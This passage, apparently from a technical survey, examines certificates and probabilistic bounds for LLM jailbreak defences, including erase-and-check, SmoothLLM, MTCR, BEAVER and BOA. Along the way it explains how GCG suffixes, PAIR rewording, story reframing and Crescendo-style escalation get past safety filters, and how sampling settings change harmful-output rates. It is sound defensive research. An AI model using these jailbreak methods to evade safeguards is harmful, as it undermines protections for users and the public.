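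Beurer-Kellner and colleagues accept that secure agents will do less. They doubt that general-purpose agents built on current language models can offer reliable guarantees, and recommend agents restricted to particular jobs. How much less these agents can do depends on how often they must choose their next action based on untrusted content. Costa and colleagues found that this is necessary in 5% of AgentDojo's workspace tasks and 10% of its travel tasks, but in about 43% of its banking and Slack tasks.

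An operator can recover some of these tasks by asking the user to confirm risky steps. But an attacker can then try to deceive the user, and people who see many confirmation requests tend to approve them without reading. The user can also defeat the labels by accident, because most of these systems trust everything in the user's prompt, including any injection the user pastes into it.

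## How far do certificates against altered prompts reach?

The software around an agent can limit its actions, but it doesn't decide whether a chatbot should answer a question. The model or a separate filter decides that, and both are neural networks that a small change to a prompt can mislead. Certified robustness is a proof that no change within a stated distance of a given prompt alters the verdict. If $F(x)$ is the verdict on prompt $x$, "harmful" or "safe", then $F$ is certified at $x_0$ with radius $r$ when

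$$F(x) = F(x_0) \quad\text{for every } x \text{ with } \mathrm{dist}(x, x_0) \le r.$$

The distance might be the number of altered characters or added words. For the film club, the reference prompt might be "How does the film end?", and the radius is how far a member's prompt can differ from it before the guarantee no longer applies.

### Erasing the attacker's words

The first certificates for jailbreaks responded to GCG (Greedy Coordinate Gradient), an automated attack that searches for a string of near-nonsense to append to a forbidden request. If an attacker only adds text, the original request is still in the prompt, and a defender can recover it by deleting the rest. Kumar, Agarwal and colleagues (2023), in *Certifying LLM Safety against Adversarial Prompting*, turned this observation into a method called erase-and-check. It needs a filter that labels any text harmful or safe, and a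 maximum number $d$ of tokens to erase:

1. Run the filter on the whole prompt.
2. Erase the last token and run the filter on the rest, then erase the last two tokens, and so on up to $d$.
3. Label the prompt harmful if the filter flagged any of these versions.

Suppose an attacker appends a string $a$ of at most $d$ tokens to a harmful request $P$. One of the shortened versions is then exactly $P$. If the filter flags $P$, erase-and-check flags the longer prompt too, whatever $a$ contains. Writing $P + a$ for the combined prompt, and counting "harmful" as 1 and "safe" as 0, we get for any collection $\mathcal{H}$ of harmful requests

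$$\mathbb{E}_{P \sim \mathcal{H}}\big[\text{erase-and-check}(P + a)\big] \;\ge\; \mathbb{E}_{P \sim \mathcal{H}}\big[\text{filter}(P)\big] \quad\text{whenever } |a| \le d.$$

The detection rate under the worst possible suffix is thus at least the filter's ordinary detection rate, which a tester can measure without running any attacks. With Llama 2 as the filter, that rate was 92% on 520 requests from AdvBench, a public collection of harmful requests. A small classifier trained for the purpose detected all 120 of its test requests. The certificate is an improvement because, without the erasing step, GCG reduced that classifier's detection rate to zero with only 12 added tokens.

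With $d = 20$, every prompt requires up to 21 runs of the filter, and each run can raise a false alarm. For example, erasing the last five words of a film club member's prompt "Tell me how the film ends up on so many lists" leaves "Tell me how the film ends", which the filter might flag. In the tests, erase-and-check still labelled 97% of harmless prompts correctly with Llama 2 and 98% with the trained classifier, whose training data included shortened harmless prompts.

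Checking takes far more computation if the attacker can add tokens anywhere, because the defender must then try erasing every set of up to $d$ tokens. For $d = 6$, a prompt of 20 tokens has 60,460 such versions, and one of 40 tokens has about 4.6 million. Even with the small classifier, the average time per prompt rose from 0.01 seconds with no erasing to 28 seconds with up to six tokens erased. Kumar and colleagues also tested a shortcut for suffixes that checks a random 30% of the shortened versions. It caught more than 90% of GCG attacks but has no certificate, because it can skip the version with exactly the attacker's suffix removed.

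The theorem covers only added text. The bedtime-story request doesn't contain the original question, so erasing parts of it can't recover that question. The filter would have to detect the story request itself, and an attacker can keep rewording it until the filter misses it. The 92% is an average over AdvBench, and the theorem gives no protection for the other 8% of requests.

### SmoothLLM and its fragile attacks

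Robey, Wong and colleagues (2023), in *SmoothLLM*, took advantage of a different weakness. GCG's strings are brittle, and randomly changing 10% of their characters could reduce their success rate to below 1%. SmoothLLM therefore adds typing errors on purpose:

1. Make $N$ copies of the prompt and change a fixed percentage of the characters in each, chosen at random.
2. Run the model on every copy, and have a classifier judge whether each reply is a jailbreak.
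3. Take a majority vote and return a reply that agrees with it.

GCG succeeded 98% of the time against Vicuna and 51% against Llama 2, both small open models. With more than six copies, SmoothLLM reduced both rates to below 1%. It helped less against PAIR, which rewrites requests in ordinary language. On Vicuna and GPT-4, PAIR still succeeded about half as often as before. SmoothLLM multiplies the number of model calls by $N$, typically up to 20, and its character changes make the model less accurate. With 20 copies and 5% of characters changed, Llama 2's score on a test of everyday physical reasoning fell from 76.7% to 70.3%.

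The certificate assumes that the attack string is "$k$-unstable", meaning that it works if fewer than $k$ of its characters change and fails if $k$ or more do. Let $\alpha$ be the probability that one altered copy doesn't produce a jailbreak. The defence succeeds if at least half the copies are safe, which has probability

$$\sum_{t=\lceil N/2\rceil}^{N} \binom{N}{t}\,\alpha^{t}(1-\alpha)^{N-t}.$$

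Under the assumption, we can calculate $\alpha$ exactly by counting how often at least $k$ of the random changes land in the attack string. But the certificate covers only attacks that have a particular weakness, and attackers can look for strings that don't. *Towards the Worst-case Robustness of Large Language Models* (Chen, Wei and colleagues, 2025) reports that a stronger search against the complete defended system got past SmoothLLM in 32% to 38% of cases on three small models.

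### Replacing the assumption with an estimate

Kumarappan and Mehrotra (2025), in *Towards Realistic Guarantees*, checked whether attacks really stop working after $k$ changes. They changed characters at random in attack strings from GCG and PAIR and measured how often the attacks still succeeded. For GCG on Llama 2, the success rate after $i$ changes closely followed the curve

$$0.292\,e^{-0.376\,i} + 0.013.$$

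The rate falls quickly but levels off at about 1.3%, so a few attacks still succeed after almost any number of character changes. Kumarappan and Mehrotra therefore call an attack string "$(k, \varepsilon)$-unstable" if it succeeds with probability at most $\varepsilon$ once $k$ or more of its characters have changed.

The new bound follows in two steps. Let the prompt have $L$ characters, $A$ of them in the attack string, and let SmoothLLM change $M$ characters in each copy. The number $X$ of changes that land in the attack string varies from copy to copy. When $X \ge k$, the copy is safe with probability at least $1 - \varepsilon$. When $X < k$, we assume the worst and count the copy as jailbroken. This gives

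$$\alpha \;\ge\; (1-\varepsilon)\,\Pr[X \ge k], \qquad \Pr[X \ge k] \;=\; 1 - \sum_{i=0}^{k-1} \frac{\binom{A}{i}\binom{L-A}{M-i}}{\binom{L}{M}}.$$

The voting formula increases with $\alpha$, so inserting this lower limit gives a lower limit on the defence's success.

In the paper's example, an operator accepts $\varepsilon = 0.05$, and the fitted curve drops below that value at $k = 6$. The attack string makes up 100 of the prompt's 240 characters, and each copy has 24 changes. On average ten of these land in the attack string, and the probability that at least six do is 0.978, so $\alpha \ge 0.929$. With ten copies, which the paper describes as typically enough for a 95% target, the formula gives a success rate of 99.998%.

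That figure is too optimistic, because the formula needs $\varepsilon$ to hold for each attack string separately, whereas the curve averages many strings. Suppose one string in 20 survives any set of typing errors and the other 19 never do. The average survival rate is still 5%, but SmoothLLM fails against the robust string every time, however many copies it makes. The data also come from attackers who didn't adapt to the defence, and Kumarappan and Mehrotra acknowledge that the curve may not fit other attacks or models. A jailbreak in plain English, for example, often remains readable with one character in ten altered.

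### Certificates that count altered tokens

SmoothLLM adapts a technique from image recognition called randomised smoothing, which can also produce certificates without any assumption about the attack. Chen and colleagues apply it to a detector that scores prompts from 0 (safe) to 1 (harmful). Let $g(x)$ be the detector's average score over random copies of prompt $x$ in which each token is masked with probability $\beta$. Now let an attacker replace $d$ tokens to produce $x'$. With probability $\beta^d$, the masks hide all $d$ of those positions, and the copies of $x$ and $x'$ look the same to the detector. In all other cases, we assume that the attack lowers the score from 1 to 0. Therefore

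$$g(x') \;\ge\; g(x) - (1 - \beta^d).$$

The bound holds for every possible choice of replacements, but it is weak. With $\beta = 0.1$, a prompt that scores a perfect 1 is guaranteed a score of only 0.01 after two replacements and 0.001 after three. To certify anything, the operator must flag prompts even when their average scores are extremely low. Chen and colleagues set the threshold at 0.000046, which they chose by testing harmless prompts. When they raised it to 0.1, the average radius in the configurations they checked fell to zero.

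With the low threshold and a million random copies per prompt, a detector based on GPT-4o had an average certified radius of 2.00 tokens on 50 AdvBench requests with masking, and 2.02 with random token substitution. Using the certified detector would also take a lot of computation. If the underlying detector outputs only yes or no, a score at the threshold means that it flags about one copy in 22,000, so the operator would need to run it tens of thousands of times for each incoming prompt.

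For short requests, a radius of two tokens is close to the largest that makes sense. Chen and colleagues estimated by hand how many tokens an attacker can replace in each request before the harmful meaning could disappear, and the average was 2.12. A certificate with a larger radius would require the detector to flag prompts that are no longer harmful. In the film club, replacing "end" with "start" in the reference prompt turns a forbidden question into a permitted one, while the bedtime-story request keeps the forbidden meaning but shares hardly a word with the original. Token counts are therefore a poor measure of how much a prompt's meaning has changed, and Chen and colleagues suggest that future certificates may need a distance based on meaning.

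### How safety decays over a conversation

All of these certificates are for a single prompt. In a conversation, the attacker can try again at every turn and build on the earlier replies. Multi-Turn Certified Robustness (MTCR), the framework by Liu and colleagues that uses clusters of conversations as abstract states, starts from the per-turn safety $p$. This is the lowest probability, over all safe states and all permitted messages, that the conversation is still safe after one more turn. The probability $\rho_k$ of staying safe for $k$ turns then satisfies

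$$\rho_k \ge p^k.$$

With $p = 0.95$, this bound is about 0.60 after 10 turns, 0.36 after 20 and 0.08 after 50. An operator who wants a bound of at least 0.9 can allow only two turns.

Liu and colleagues make two assumptions about the structure of conversations to get better bounds. One is that a conversation mostly stays within a cluster, which they call a mode, and that staying there is safer than moving to another. If every turn within a mode is safe with probability at least $1 - \delta$, every switch between modes is safe with probability at least $\gamma$, and there are at most $s$ switches, then for modes that don't overlap

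$$\rho_k \ge (1-\delta)^{k-s}\,\gamma^{s}.$$

Their example has 20 turns, three switches, $\delta = 0.02$ and $\gamma = 0.7$. The bound is $0.98^{17} \times 0.7^3 \approx 0.243$, about twice the simple bound $p^{20} = 0.9^{20} \approx 0.122$ that they calculate with a per-turn safety of $p = 0.9$. But the example isn't quite consistent, because $p$ is the minimum over all turns, including switches, and so can't be 0.9 if the safety of some switches is only 0.7. With $p = 0.7$, the simple bound would be about 0.0008, and the improvement would look far larger.

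Nearly all of that improvement comes from assuming at most three switches. But the attacker chooses the topic, and changing mode at every turn would bring the new bound down to $0.7^{20}$, the same 0.0008. The assumption would be safe if software enforced the limit, for example by ending the conversation at the fourth switch.

The other assumption, safety persistence, concerns the margin, which is the distance between the current state and the nearest unsafe one. From any safe state, with probability at least $b$, the next state must also be safe and keep at least a fixed fraction of the margin. This gives $\rho_k \ge b^k$, which Liu and colleagues present as an improvement whenever $b > p$. But by their own definitions $b$ can't be greater than $p$, because every turn that keeps enough of the margin is also a safe turn, so its worst-case probability can't be higher. Their values for Llama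 2, $b = 0.79$ and $p = 0.78$, are possible only because both are estimates.

They also prove that no better general bound exists without some such structure. For example, if a chatbot's next state is drawn afresh at every turn and is safe with probability $p$, whatever anyone has said before, then the probability of staying safe for $k$ turns is exactly $p^k$, so knowing only $p$ cannot justify a stronger guarantee. The two structural bounds still shrink exponentially as a conversation gets longer, though the one based on modes can shrink more slowly.

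### The results on six models

Liu and colleagues applied MTCR to six models, using 150 AdvBench requests. The table gives the probability that a model stays safe throughout a conversation. The measured figures come from a Crescendo-style attack, which escalates gradually.

| Model | $p^k$, 5 turns | MTCR bound, 5 turns | Measured, 5 turns | MTCR bound, 10 turns | Measured, 10 turns |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
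| GPT-4o | 44% | 55% | 78% | 32% | 62% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 42% | 51% | 74% | 28% | 58% |
| Qwen2.5-7B | 35% | 44% | 65% | 22% | 49% |
| Llama 3.2 3B | 33% | 40% | 62% | 18% | 45% |
| Llama 2 7B | 29% | 36% | 55% | 13% | 38% |
| Vicuna 7B | 22% | 28% | 46% | 8% | 30% |

After five turns, the MTCR bounds are about a quarter higher than $p^k$, but they are still too low to reassure an operator. Even for GPT-4o, the best of the six models, the bound is 32% after ten turns, so the chance of a harmful reply within those turns could be as high as 68%. For Llama 2, the bound is only 2% after 20 turns.

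The bounds also apply only to an attacker who changes at most five characters of a reference message at each turn, which is enough for a few typos or one short word. Allowing seven characters lowers Llama 2's five-turn bound from 36% to 24%. Real multi-turn attacks send entirely new messages that move step by step towards the forbidden subject, and Liu and colleagues state that their formal guarantee doesn't cover these.

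They report that measured safety under the Crescendo-style attack stayed above the bounds, and suggest that the structure they found may extend beyond small edits. This is weak evidence because the attack followed fixed templates, which they acknowledge makes it weaker than the original Crescendo. The original adapts to each reply and, by their account, succeeds almost every time in fewer than ten turns. At that rate, the probability of staying safe would be far below 32%. This wouldn't contradict the theorem, which doesn't cover those messages, but the bound would have no practical value against that attack.

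Even for five-character edits, the numbers in the table are estimates. The theorems require the worst case over all states and all permitted edits, but the experiments used 100 random samples per mode. A 50-character message has more than $10^{16}$ versions with exactly five characters replaced. For some parameters, Liu and colleagues use a confidence interval, which accounts for sampling error in an average but can't be used to find the worst edit.

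The formula behind the table, which combines the two assumptions, also has a problem. Multiplied out, it equals the bound from modes alone times $b^s$, so it can never give a higher value than modes alone. Yet for Llama 2 over five turns, the paper reports 36% for the combined formula and 34% for modes alone, so the two figures can't come from the same parameters.

### Attempts to certify against paraphrase

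Jailbreaks that work through meaning don't need to stay near any reference prompt. *Breaking the Assumptions* (2026), an audit of defences that alter or inspect the prompt, notes that such attacks are designed to violate the certificates' assumptions. Several recent papers try to account for meaning in their certificates, but these cover far fewer inputs than the set of all paraphrases.

*CluCERT* (2025) smooths a classifier by replacing words with synonyms. It takes the synonyms from WordNet, a dictionary database, and checks that their embeddings are similar. It calculates the certified radius on a filtered version of the prompt that is meant to keep the core content. Synonym swaps are closer to ordinary rewording than random characters are, but the guarantee still covers only changes within the radius, and turning a question into a story goes far beyond swapping synonyms.

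*Provable Defense Framework for LLM Jailbreaks via Noise-Augumented Alignment* (2026) presents a method called Certified Semantic Smoothing. "Semantic" refers to the tokens that carry a prompt's content rather than only its structure. The certificate gives the number of content tokens an attacker may edit. It relies on taking random samples of those tokens, because some samples will contain no edits. If a prompt has 20 content tokens, the attacker edits three, and each sample keeps five, about 40% of samples are unaffected. If a paraphrase replaces all 20, every sample is affected and there is no guarantee.

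A defender can also make the random copies by paraphrasing, as *Defending Large Language Models against Jailbreak Attacks via Semantic Smoothing* (2024) does with rewordings and summaries. This worked well in tests on three models and three attacks. Turning it into a certificate is hard, because a smoothing proof has to show how much the copies of the original prompt overlap with the copies of the attacker's prompt. The overlap is $\beta^d$ with random masks, but when a language model writes the copies, nobody knows how to calculate it for every prompt an attacker might send.

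*Guarding the Meaning* (2025) trains a safety classifier to give the same score to different paraphrases of a chatbot reply. A language model writes the paraphrases, and another model discards those that change the meaning. This training can make a classifier more consistent, but its consistency is measured only on the generated paraphrases, and the models that write and filter them can make mistakes.

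Kezins, Ekka and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Red-Teaming*, avoid defining paraphrase altogether. A neural classifier turns each text into an embedding before its last layer calculates a score. The researchers fed 10,000 toxic texts to a classifier and drew a multidimensional box around the resulting points. The last layer computes a weighted sum and converts it into a score that rises with the sum, so the lowest score in the box is easy to find. If coordinate $i$ ranges from $l_i$ to $u_i$ and has weight $w_i$, the smallest possible sum is

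$$z_{\min} = \sum_i \min(w_i l_i,\; w_i u_i) + c,$$

where $c$ is a constant. If the score for $z_{\min}$ is above the threshold, the classifier flags every point in the box.

All three trained classifiers failed this check, both with one large box and with several small ones. They included the classifier based on Llama 3.1 8B, which had caught all 100 toxic texts in an ordinary test. The boxes only partly explain the failures, because some of the toxic texts used to draw them scored between 0.002 and 0.070, far below the thresholds, and a box that contains even one missed text must fail.

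Kezins and colleagues then replaced the boxes with bell-shaped distributions fitted to the same points and calculated what share of each distribution the classifier flags. The share was 90% for a classifier based on GPT-2, 80% for the Llama one and 55% for one based on BERT, an older language model. Lowering the threshold raised the BERT figure to 100%, but the classifier then also flagged 59 of 100 harmless texts. These percentages are averages over a fitted distribution, so they don't guarantee protection against an attacker who looks for prompts the classifier misses.

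Passing the box check would not have proved that a classifier catches paraphrases either. For the Llama classifier, a single box contained only 23% of held-out toxic texts, and nobody has proved where the network maps a paraphrase. An operator can find out whether a given paraphrase lands in the box only by running the classifier on it, which already gives the verdict.

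## Can the probability of a harmful output be bounded?

Certificates against altered prompts cover the inputs near a given prompt. We can also keep the prompt fixed and ask how likely a harmful reply is. A chatbot's replies are partly random, so one that refuses a request nine times may comply the tenth time. But at each step the model calculates a probability for every possible next token, and anyone who runs the model can read these probabilities. A program could therefore in principle calculate $v(x)$, the probability of a violation for a fixed prompt $x$, without sampling replies.

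### A tree of possible replies

The possible replies to a prompt form a tree. The root is the empty reply, each branch adds a token, and a path ends when the model produces a marker for the end of the text. The probability of a beginning $s = t_1 t_2 \dots t_n$ is the product of the probabilities along its path:

$$\mu(s) = \prod_{i=1}^{n} P(t_i \mid x\, t_1 \cdots t_{i-1}).$$

$v(x)$ is the sum of $\mu(s)$ over all complete replies that break the rule. The whole tree is far too large to explore, but exploring a small part of it is enough to give lower and upper bounds on $v(x)$.

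Suppose the murderer in the film is the gardener, and the club forbids the chatbot to write the word "gardener". A member asks how the film ends. A program runs the model three times to find which words can come first, which can follow "Sorry" and which can follow "The". In this simplified example, only a few words are possible at each point.

| Beginning of the reply | Probability | Status |
|---|---|---|
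| "Sorry", then the end | 0.80 × 0.90 = 0.72 | finished and harmless |
| "Sorry but" | 0.80 × 0.10 = 0.08 | unfinished |
| "The gardener" | 0.15 × 0.40 = 0.06 | violation |
| "The ending" | 0.15 × 0.60 = 0.09 | unfinished |
| "Well" | 0.05 | unfinished |

The probability of a violation is at least 6%, because 6% of replies begin "The gardener", which breaks the rule however the reply continues. It is at most 28%, because 72% of replies are finished and harmless. The 22-point gap is the total probability of the unfinished beginnings. Each further run of the model splits one of these beginnings into longer ones, so the bounds can only tighten. Both bounds are certain, unlike the 95% confidence limits from testing a sample of replies.

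### Branch and bound with BEAVER

Suresh, Wadhwa and colleagues (2025), in *BEAVER*, turn this idea into a practical program. BEAVER stores the harmless beginnings in a tree and keeps track of its leaves, which they call the frontier. It uses branch and bound, a standard search method that splits a problem into parts and drops each part once its answer is known:

1. Choose the unfinished beginning with the highest probability.
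2. Run the model once to get the probabilities of all possible next tokens.
3. Drop the continuations that break the rule, add the others to the frontier and recalculate the bounds.

To save memory, BEAVER also discards very unlikely continuations, but it keeps a running total $M$ of their probability. If $C$ is the set of finished harmless replies and $U$ the set of unfinished beginnings, the bounds are

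$$1 - \sum_{s \in C \cup U} \mu(s) - M \;\le\; v(x) \;\le\; 1 - \sum_{s \in C} \mu(s).$$

Both bounds remain valid when text is discarded, because the lower bound counts all unfinished or discarded text as harmless and the upper bound counts it as harmful.

BEAVER requires the rule to be a safety property that a program can check on every prefix of a reply. It also needs the model's full token probabilities, which providers of closed models don't reveal.

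Suresh and colleagues tested 12 open models on four rules. The model must not reveal a person's email address, write insecure code, use stereotypes or write toxic text. An automatic detector for each rule judged whether the output broke it. BEAVER could run the model up to 100 times per prompt and stopped early if the gap between the bounds fell below one percentage point. Each cell gives the share of prompts for which BEAVER proved a violation probability of at least 10%, followed by the average number of runs.

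| Model | Email addresses | Insecure code | Stereotypes | Toxicity |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.2 3B | 9% / 99 | 8% / 99 | 3% / 99 | 6% / 99 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66% / 39 | 12% / 99 | 0.3% / 99 | 3% / 99 |
| Qwen3 4B | 63% / 11 | 44% / 92 | 0% / 48 | 0% / 71 |
| Qwen3 30B | 69% / 11 | 50% / 96 | 1% / 86 | 2% / 79 |
| Qwen2.5 7B | 65% / 16 | 45% / 96 | 1% / 99 | 58% / 86 |
| Qwen2.5 14B | 65% / 16 | 40% / 98 | 49% / 69 | 59% / 89 |
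| Gemma 3 4B | 59% / 26 | 41% / 87 | 61% / 97 | 65% / 76 |
| Gemma 3 12B | 64% / 24 | 57% / 86 | 12% / 99 | 50% / 88 |
| Phi-4 14B | 57% / 83 | 14% / 99 | 0% / 99 | 0% / 99 |
| Phi-4 mini | 53% / 92 | 5% / 99 | 0% / 99 | 0% / 99 |
| OLMo 3 7B | 68% / 42 | 15% / 99 | 24% / 99 | 3% / 99 |
| Mistral Nemo | 66% / 59 | 10% / 80 | 82% / 98 | 2% / 99 |

A low percentage does not prove that a model is safe, although a high one does prove risk. Phi-4 has 0% for stereotypes and toxicity, and Suresh and colleagues count these among its safe tasks. But BEAVER used nearly all of its 100 runs on them, so for most of these prompts it stopped with a wide gap between its bounds, and the true probability of a violation could be above 10%. Suresh and colleagues make the same point about Llama 3.2 3B, whose low figures may only reflect loose bounds. Qwen3 4B's 0% for stereotypes is better evidence, because an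 average of 48 runs means that the bounds met early for many prompts.

The comparison method samples complete replies and adds up the probabilities of the distinct ones. With ten times as many runs on six of the models, it identified 8.8% of the code prompts as risky, compared with 25.0% for BEAVER. On the email task, where replies have at most 16 tokens, the two methods did equally well. This comparison understates what sampling can do, because the method does not use the frequency of violations. A thousand runs produce about 31 replies of 32 tokens. If nine of them broke the rule, an ordinary confidence interval would put the violation rate above 14%, with 95% confidence rather than certainty.

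Length is the main obstacle to a useful upper bound. Replies in the other three tasks had at most 32 or 48 tokens. If the most likely token has a probability of 0.9 at every step, the most likely 16-token reply has a probability of about 19%, and a few such replies can account for most of the total probability. The most likely 500-token reply would have a probability of about $10^{-23}$, so a program would have to finish an astronomical number of harmless replies before the upper bound fell noticeably below 100%. A lower bound can still be useful for long replies, because a violation may appear within the first few words.

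### What a cut tree leaves out

*Bounded PCTL Model Checking of Large Language Model Outputs* (Gross, Spieker and Gotlieb, 2025) shrinks the tree before analysing it. Its tool, LLMchecker, keeps only the most likely tokens at each step, stopping when their total probability reaches a threshold $\alpha$ or when it has $k$ of them. It sends the remaining probability to a dead-end state. This produces a small Markov chain that a standard model checker can search exhaustively. LLMchecker takes queries in PCTL, a temporal logic with probabilities, in which $P(\mathbf{F}\,\varphi)$ is the probability that $\varphi$ becomes true at some point.

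In one test, Gross and colleagues calculated how likely several models were to continue "The player won because" with text that leans towards male terms. For Mistral 7B, with $\alpha = 0.8$, $k = 15$ and only five new tokens, the chain had 255,085 states, took more than 13 hours to build and check, and gave a probability of 3.65%. In another test, the probability that Gemma 7B would continue the first words of *Lolita* with text close to the original was 33%, compared with 6% for the smaller Gemma 2B. None of the tests involved jailbreaks, and the longest outputs had ten tokens.

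LLMchecker's answers are exact for the cut tree, but the real model can also choose the discarded tokens. If the cut keeps 80% of the probability at each of five steps, the surviving paths have a total probability of only $0.8^5 \approx 33\%$. The other 67% could contain any number of violations, so a result of zero does not rule them out. When the question is whether something bad eventually happens, the result is a lower bound, and adding the probability of the discarded paths gives an upper bound. BEAVER calculates both bounds automatically. The loss was small in one of LLMchecker's own comparisons, where reducing $k$ from 32,000 to 9 for two tokens from Gemma 2B lowered the number of states from 9,637 to 499 and the calculated probability from 0.5% to 0.4%.

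The cut doesn't affect the guarantee if the deployed software makes the same cut. Many systems use top-$k$ sampling, which chooses only among the $k$ most likely tokens, or top-$p$ sampling, which chooses among the most likely tokens whose probabilities add up to $p$. Once the software rescales the remaining probabilities, the cut tree matches the outputs the system can produce and their probabilities. The guarantee then depends on those settings staying the same.

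### Looking for rare harmful replies

BEAVER starts with the most probable text, but a well-trained model's harmful replies are usually improbable. Nazeri, Schmuck and colleagues (2026) therefore direct the search towards harmful replies in *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models*. They collect 64 harmful and 64 harmless replies to a prompt from an unrestricted model, run both groups through the model under test, and take the difference between the average internal states as a "harmful direction". The search prefers beginnings of replies that are both fairly probable and close to this direction, and adds up the probabilities of the harmful ones it finds. The direction can be wrong without affecting the proof, because the sum from any partial search is a valid lower bound on the probability of a harmful output.

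The table compares this lower bound with a 95% confidence upper bound from ordinary sampling. Each method could generate up to 1,000 tokens in total, and the software chose among the ten most likely tokens at each step. Sampling produced no harmful replies in any of these tests, so its lower bound was zero.

| Request | Model | Lower bound from the search | Upper bound from sampling |
|---|---|---|---|
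| Ingredients of an explosive, for a peaceful purpose | Phi-4 | $2.3 \times 10^{-14}$ | 26.4% |
| Ingredients of an explosive, for a bomb | Llama 3.2 3B | $4.3 \times 10^{-7}$ | 5.2% |
| Software for breaking into Wi-Fi | Llama 3.2 3B | $7.9 \times 10^{-10}$ | 9.2% |
| Ways to rob a bank | Llama 3.2 3B | $1.8 \times 10^{-8}$ | 10.2% |

For the bomb request, the true probability could be anywhere between one in 2.4 million and one in 19. The search proves that the model can produce a harmful reply and supplies examples that developers can use for further training. But it cannot certify that a model is safe, because that requires an upper bound. The upper bounds in the table are high because 1,000 tokens make up very few replies. Phi-4's upper bound of 26.4% is what 12 clean replies would give. A tester would need about 8.7 million clean replies to bring the upper bound for the bomb request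 down to the lower bound.

In the first three tests, a reply also counted as harmful if it contained any of three listed terms. A refusal that mentions one of those terms would also count as harmful, so even the lower bounds apply to the probability of matching the word list, not directly to the probability of harm.

*Estimating Tail Risks in Language Model Output Distributions* (2026) uses importance sampling to reduce the number of samples needed. The researchers draw replies from deliberately unsafe versions of the model, which produce harmful replies more often, and weight each reply by how much less likely the real model is to produce it. This estimates the probability of a harmful reply but doesn't prove an upper bound on it.

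### Is any sufficiently likely reply harmful?

Lin, Suri and colleagues (2025), in *Toward Principled LLM Safety Testing*, pose a yes-or-no version of the problem, which they call the jailbreak oracle problem. Given a model, a prompt, the sampling settings and a judge, is there a single harmful reply whose probability exceeds a threshold? Since every long reply is improbable, the threshold has to fall with length. For a reply $r$ of $n$ tokens, the condition is

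$$\mu(r) \ge \varepsilon \cdot L_n,$$

where $L_n$ is the average probability of the first $n$ tokens of an ordinary reply. With $\varepsilon = 1$, a harmful reply must be at least as likely as an ordinary one of the same length, and with $\varepsilon = 10^{-4}$ it can be 10,000 times less likely.

BOA first samples ten replies. If none is harmful, it searches the tree, extending the partial replies that a scoring model rates most promising. For the first 20 tokens, it gives unlikely words the same chance as likely ones, because safety training mostly affects how a reply starts. If BOA finds a harmful reply, the answer is a definite "yes" that anyone can check, subject to the judge's accuracy. It can answer "no" only after finishing the search.

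With $\varepsilon = 10^{-4}$ and ten minutes per prompt, the share of 128 prompts for which BOA found a harmful reply ranged from 7% for Llama 2 to 95% for Vicuna. For Llama 3.1 8B, it found one for 24% of prompts, compared with 12% for plain sampling that processed as many tokens. It ran out of time on another 70% and completed the search without finding a harmful reply for only eight prompts. For the larger Llama 3.1 70B, whose replies branch less, it completed the search without finding one for 58 prompts.

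Even a completed search doesn't bound $v(x)$, because the threshold applies to each reply separately. A million different harmful replies, each with a probability of one in two million, would together make up half of the model's output. Lin and colleagues describe $\varepsilon = 10^{-4}$ as covering jailbreaks that may appear once in 10,000 generations. That would be right only if an ordinary reply had a probability close to one, but a specific reply of 100 tokens is usually far less likely.

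The most useful result from BOA for operators may be the effect of the sampling settings. With its default top-$p$ setting, Llama 3.1 8B gave a harmful reply to 24% of the prompts within the time limit. With top-$k$ sampling, the figure was above 90% for every $k$ tested, even $k = 5$. When the model is almost certain to refuse, top-$p$ leaves only refusals to choose from, while top-$k$ always keeps $k$ options. For 30 of the 128 prompts, BOA found no harmful reply under the default settings but found one under every alternative tested, so a bound proved for one setting need not hold for another.

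### From one prompt to a distribution of prompts

An operator also needs to know about prompts that nobody has analysed yet. The usual approach is to define a probability distribution over prompts, draw independent samples and compute a confidence interval for the rate of violations. Most of the work described here uses the Clopper–Pearson interval. If $m$ of $n$ samples are violations, its 95% version runs from the rate $\underline p$ at which $m$ or more violations would have probability 2.5% to the rate $\overline p$ at which $m$ or fewer would:

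$$\sum_{j=m}^{n}\binom{n}{j}\underline p^{\,j}(1-\underline p)^{n-j} = 0.025, \qquad \sum_{j=0}^{m}\binom{n}{j}\overline p^{\,j}(1-\overline p)^{n-j} = 0.025.$$

Wang, Chaudhary and colleagues (2025), in *Quantifying Risks in Multi-turn Conversation with Large Language Models*, apply it to whole conversations. They start with 68 harmful goals from HarmBench, 28 on chemical and biological weapons and 40 on cybercrime. For each goal, three language models write less harmful questions on related subjects, such as the career of a historical chemist. The researchers keep 100 questions per goal and link those with similar meanings in a graph. A random process then picks the questions for each conversation.

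One version picks questions independently and sometimes puts a known jailbreak text before them. Another follows links in the graph, with or without a final question close to the harmful goal. An adaptive version tends to move towards the goal when the model answers and away from it when the model refuses. For each goal and version, Wang and colleagues sampled 50 conversations and had GPT-4o judge the replies. The table gives the median lower and upper limits for models from 2024 and 2025.

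| Model | Weapons, random with jailbreaks | Weapons, adaptive | Cybercrime, random with jailbreaks | Cybercrime, adaptive |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 0.1–10.6% | 0.1–10.6% | 2.8–20.5% | 19.5–46.7% |
| gpt-oss-120b | 2.8–20.5% | 10.1–33.7% | 8.6–31.4% | 31.8–60.7% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 21.2–48.8% | 14.6–40.3% | 37.4–66.3% | 39.3–68.2% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 55.4–82.1% | 21.2–48.8% | 72.1–93.5% | 54.3–81.3% |
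| Mistral Large | 55.4–82.1% | 45.2–73.5% | 65.2–89.2% | 56.5–83.0% |

The choice of distribution matters. On cybercrime, switching from random to adaptive questions makes Claude look much worse and DeepSeek look better. The researchers chose the distribution by setting the similarity limits for the graph, giving every permitted question the same probability (apart from the adaptive version's preferences) and deciding how the process reacts to refusals. The intervals are valid for conversations drawn this way. A real attacker can ask other questions, so even the adaptive version covers only one random strategy and not the best possible one.

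The intervals are also wide because each is based on only 50 samples. Even 50 conversations without a violation would leave an upper limit of 7.1%. The 95% guarantee applies to each interval separately, and there are 1,360 of them (68 goals, four versions and five models), so dozens could miss the true value.

*Lumos* (Chaudhary, Jain and colleagues, 2025) provides a programming language for defining such distributions. The user describes a graph of possible prompt parts and how to sample from it, and Lumos draws independent prompts and computes the interval. A short Lumos program can express the conversation tests just described. The user still has to choose the distribution, but the program makes that choice explicit, so other people can inspect or change it.

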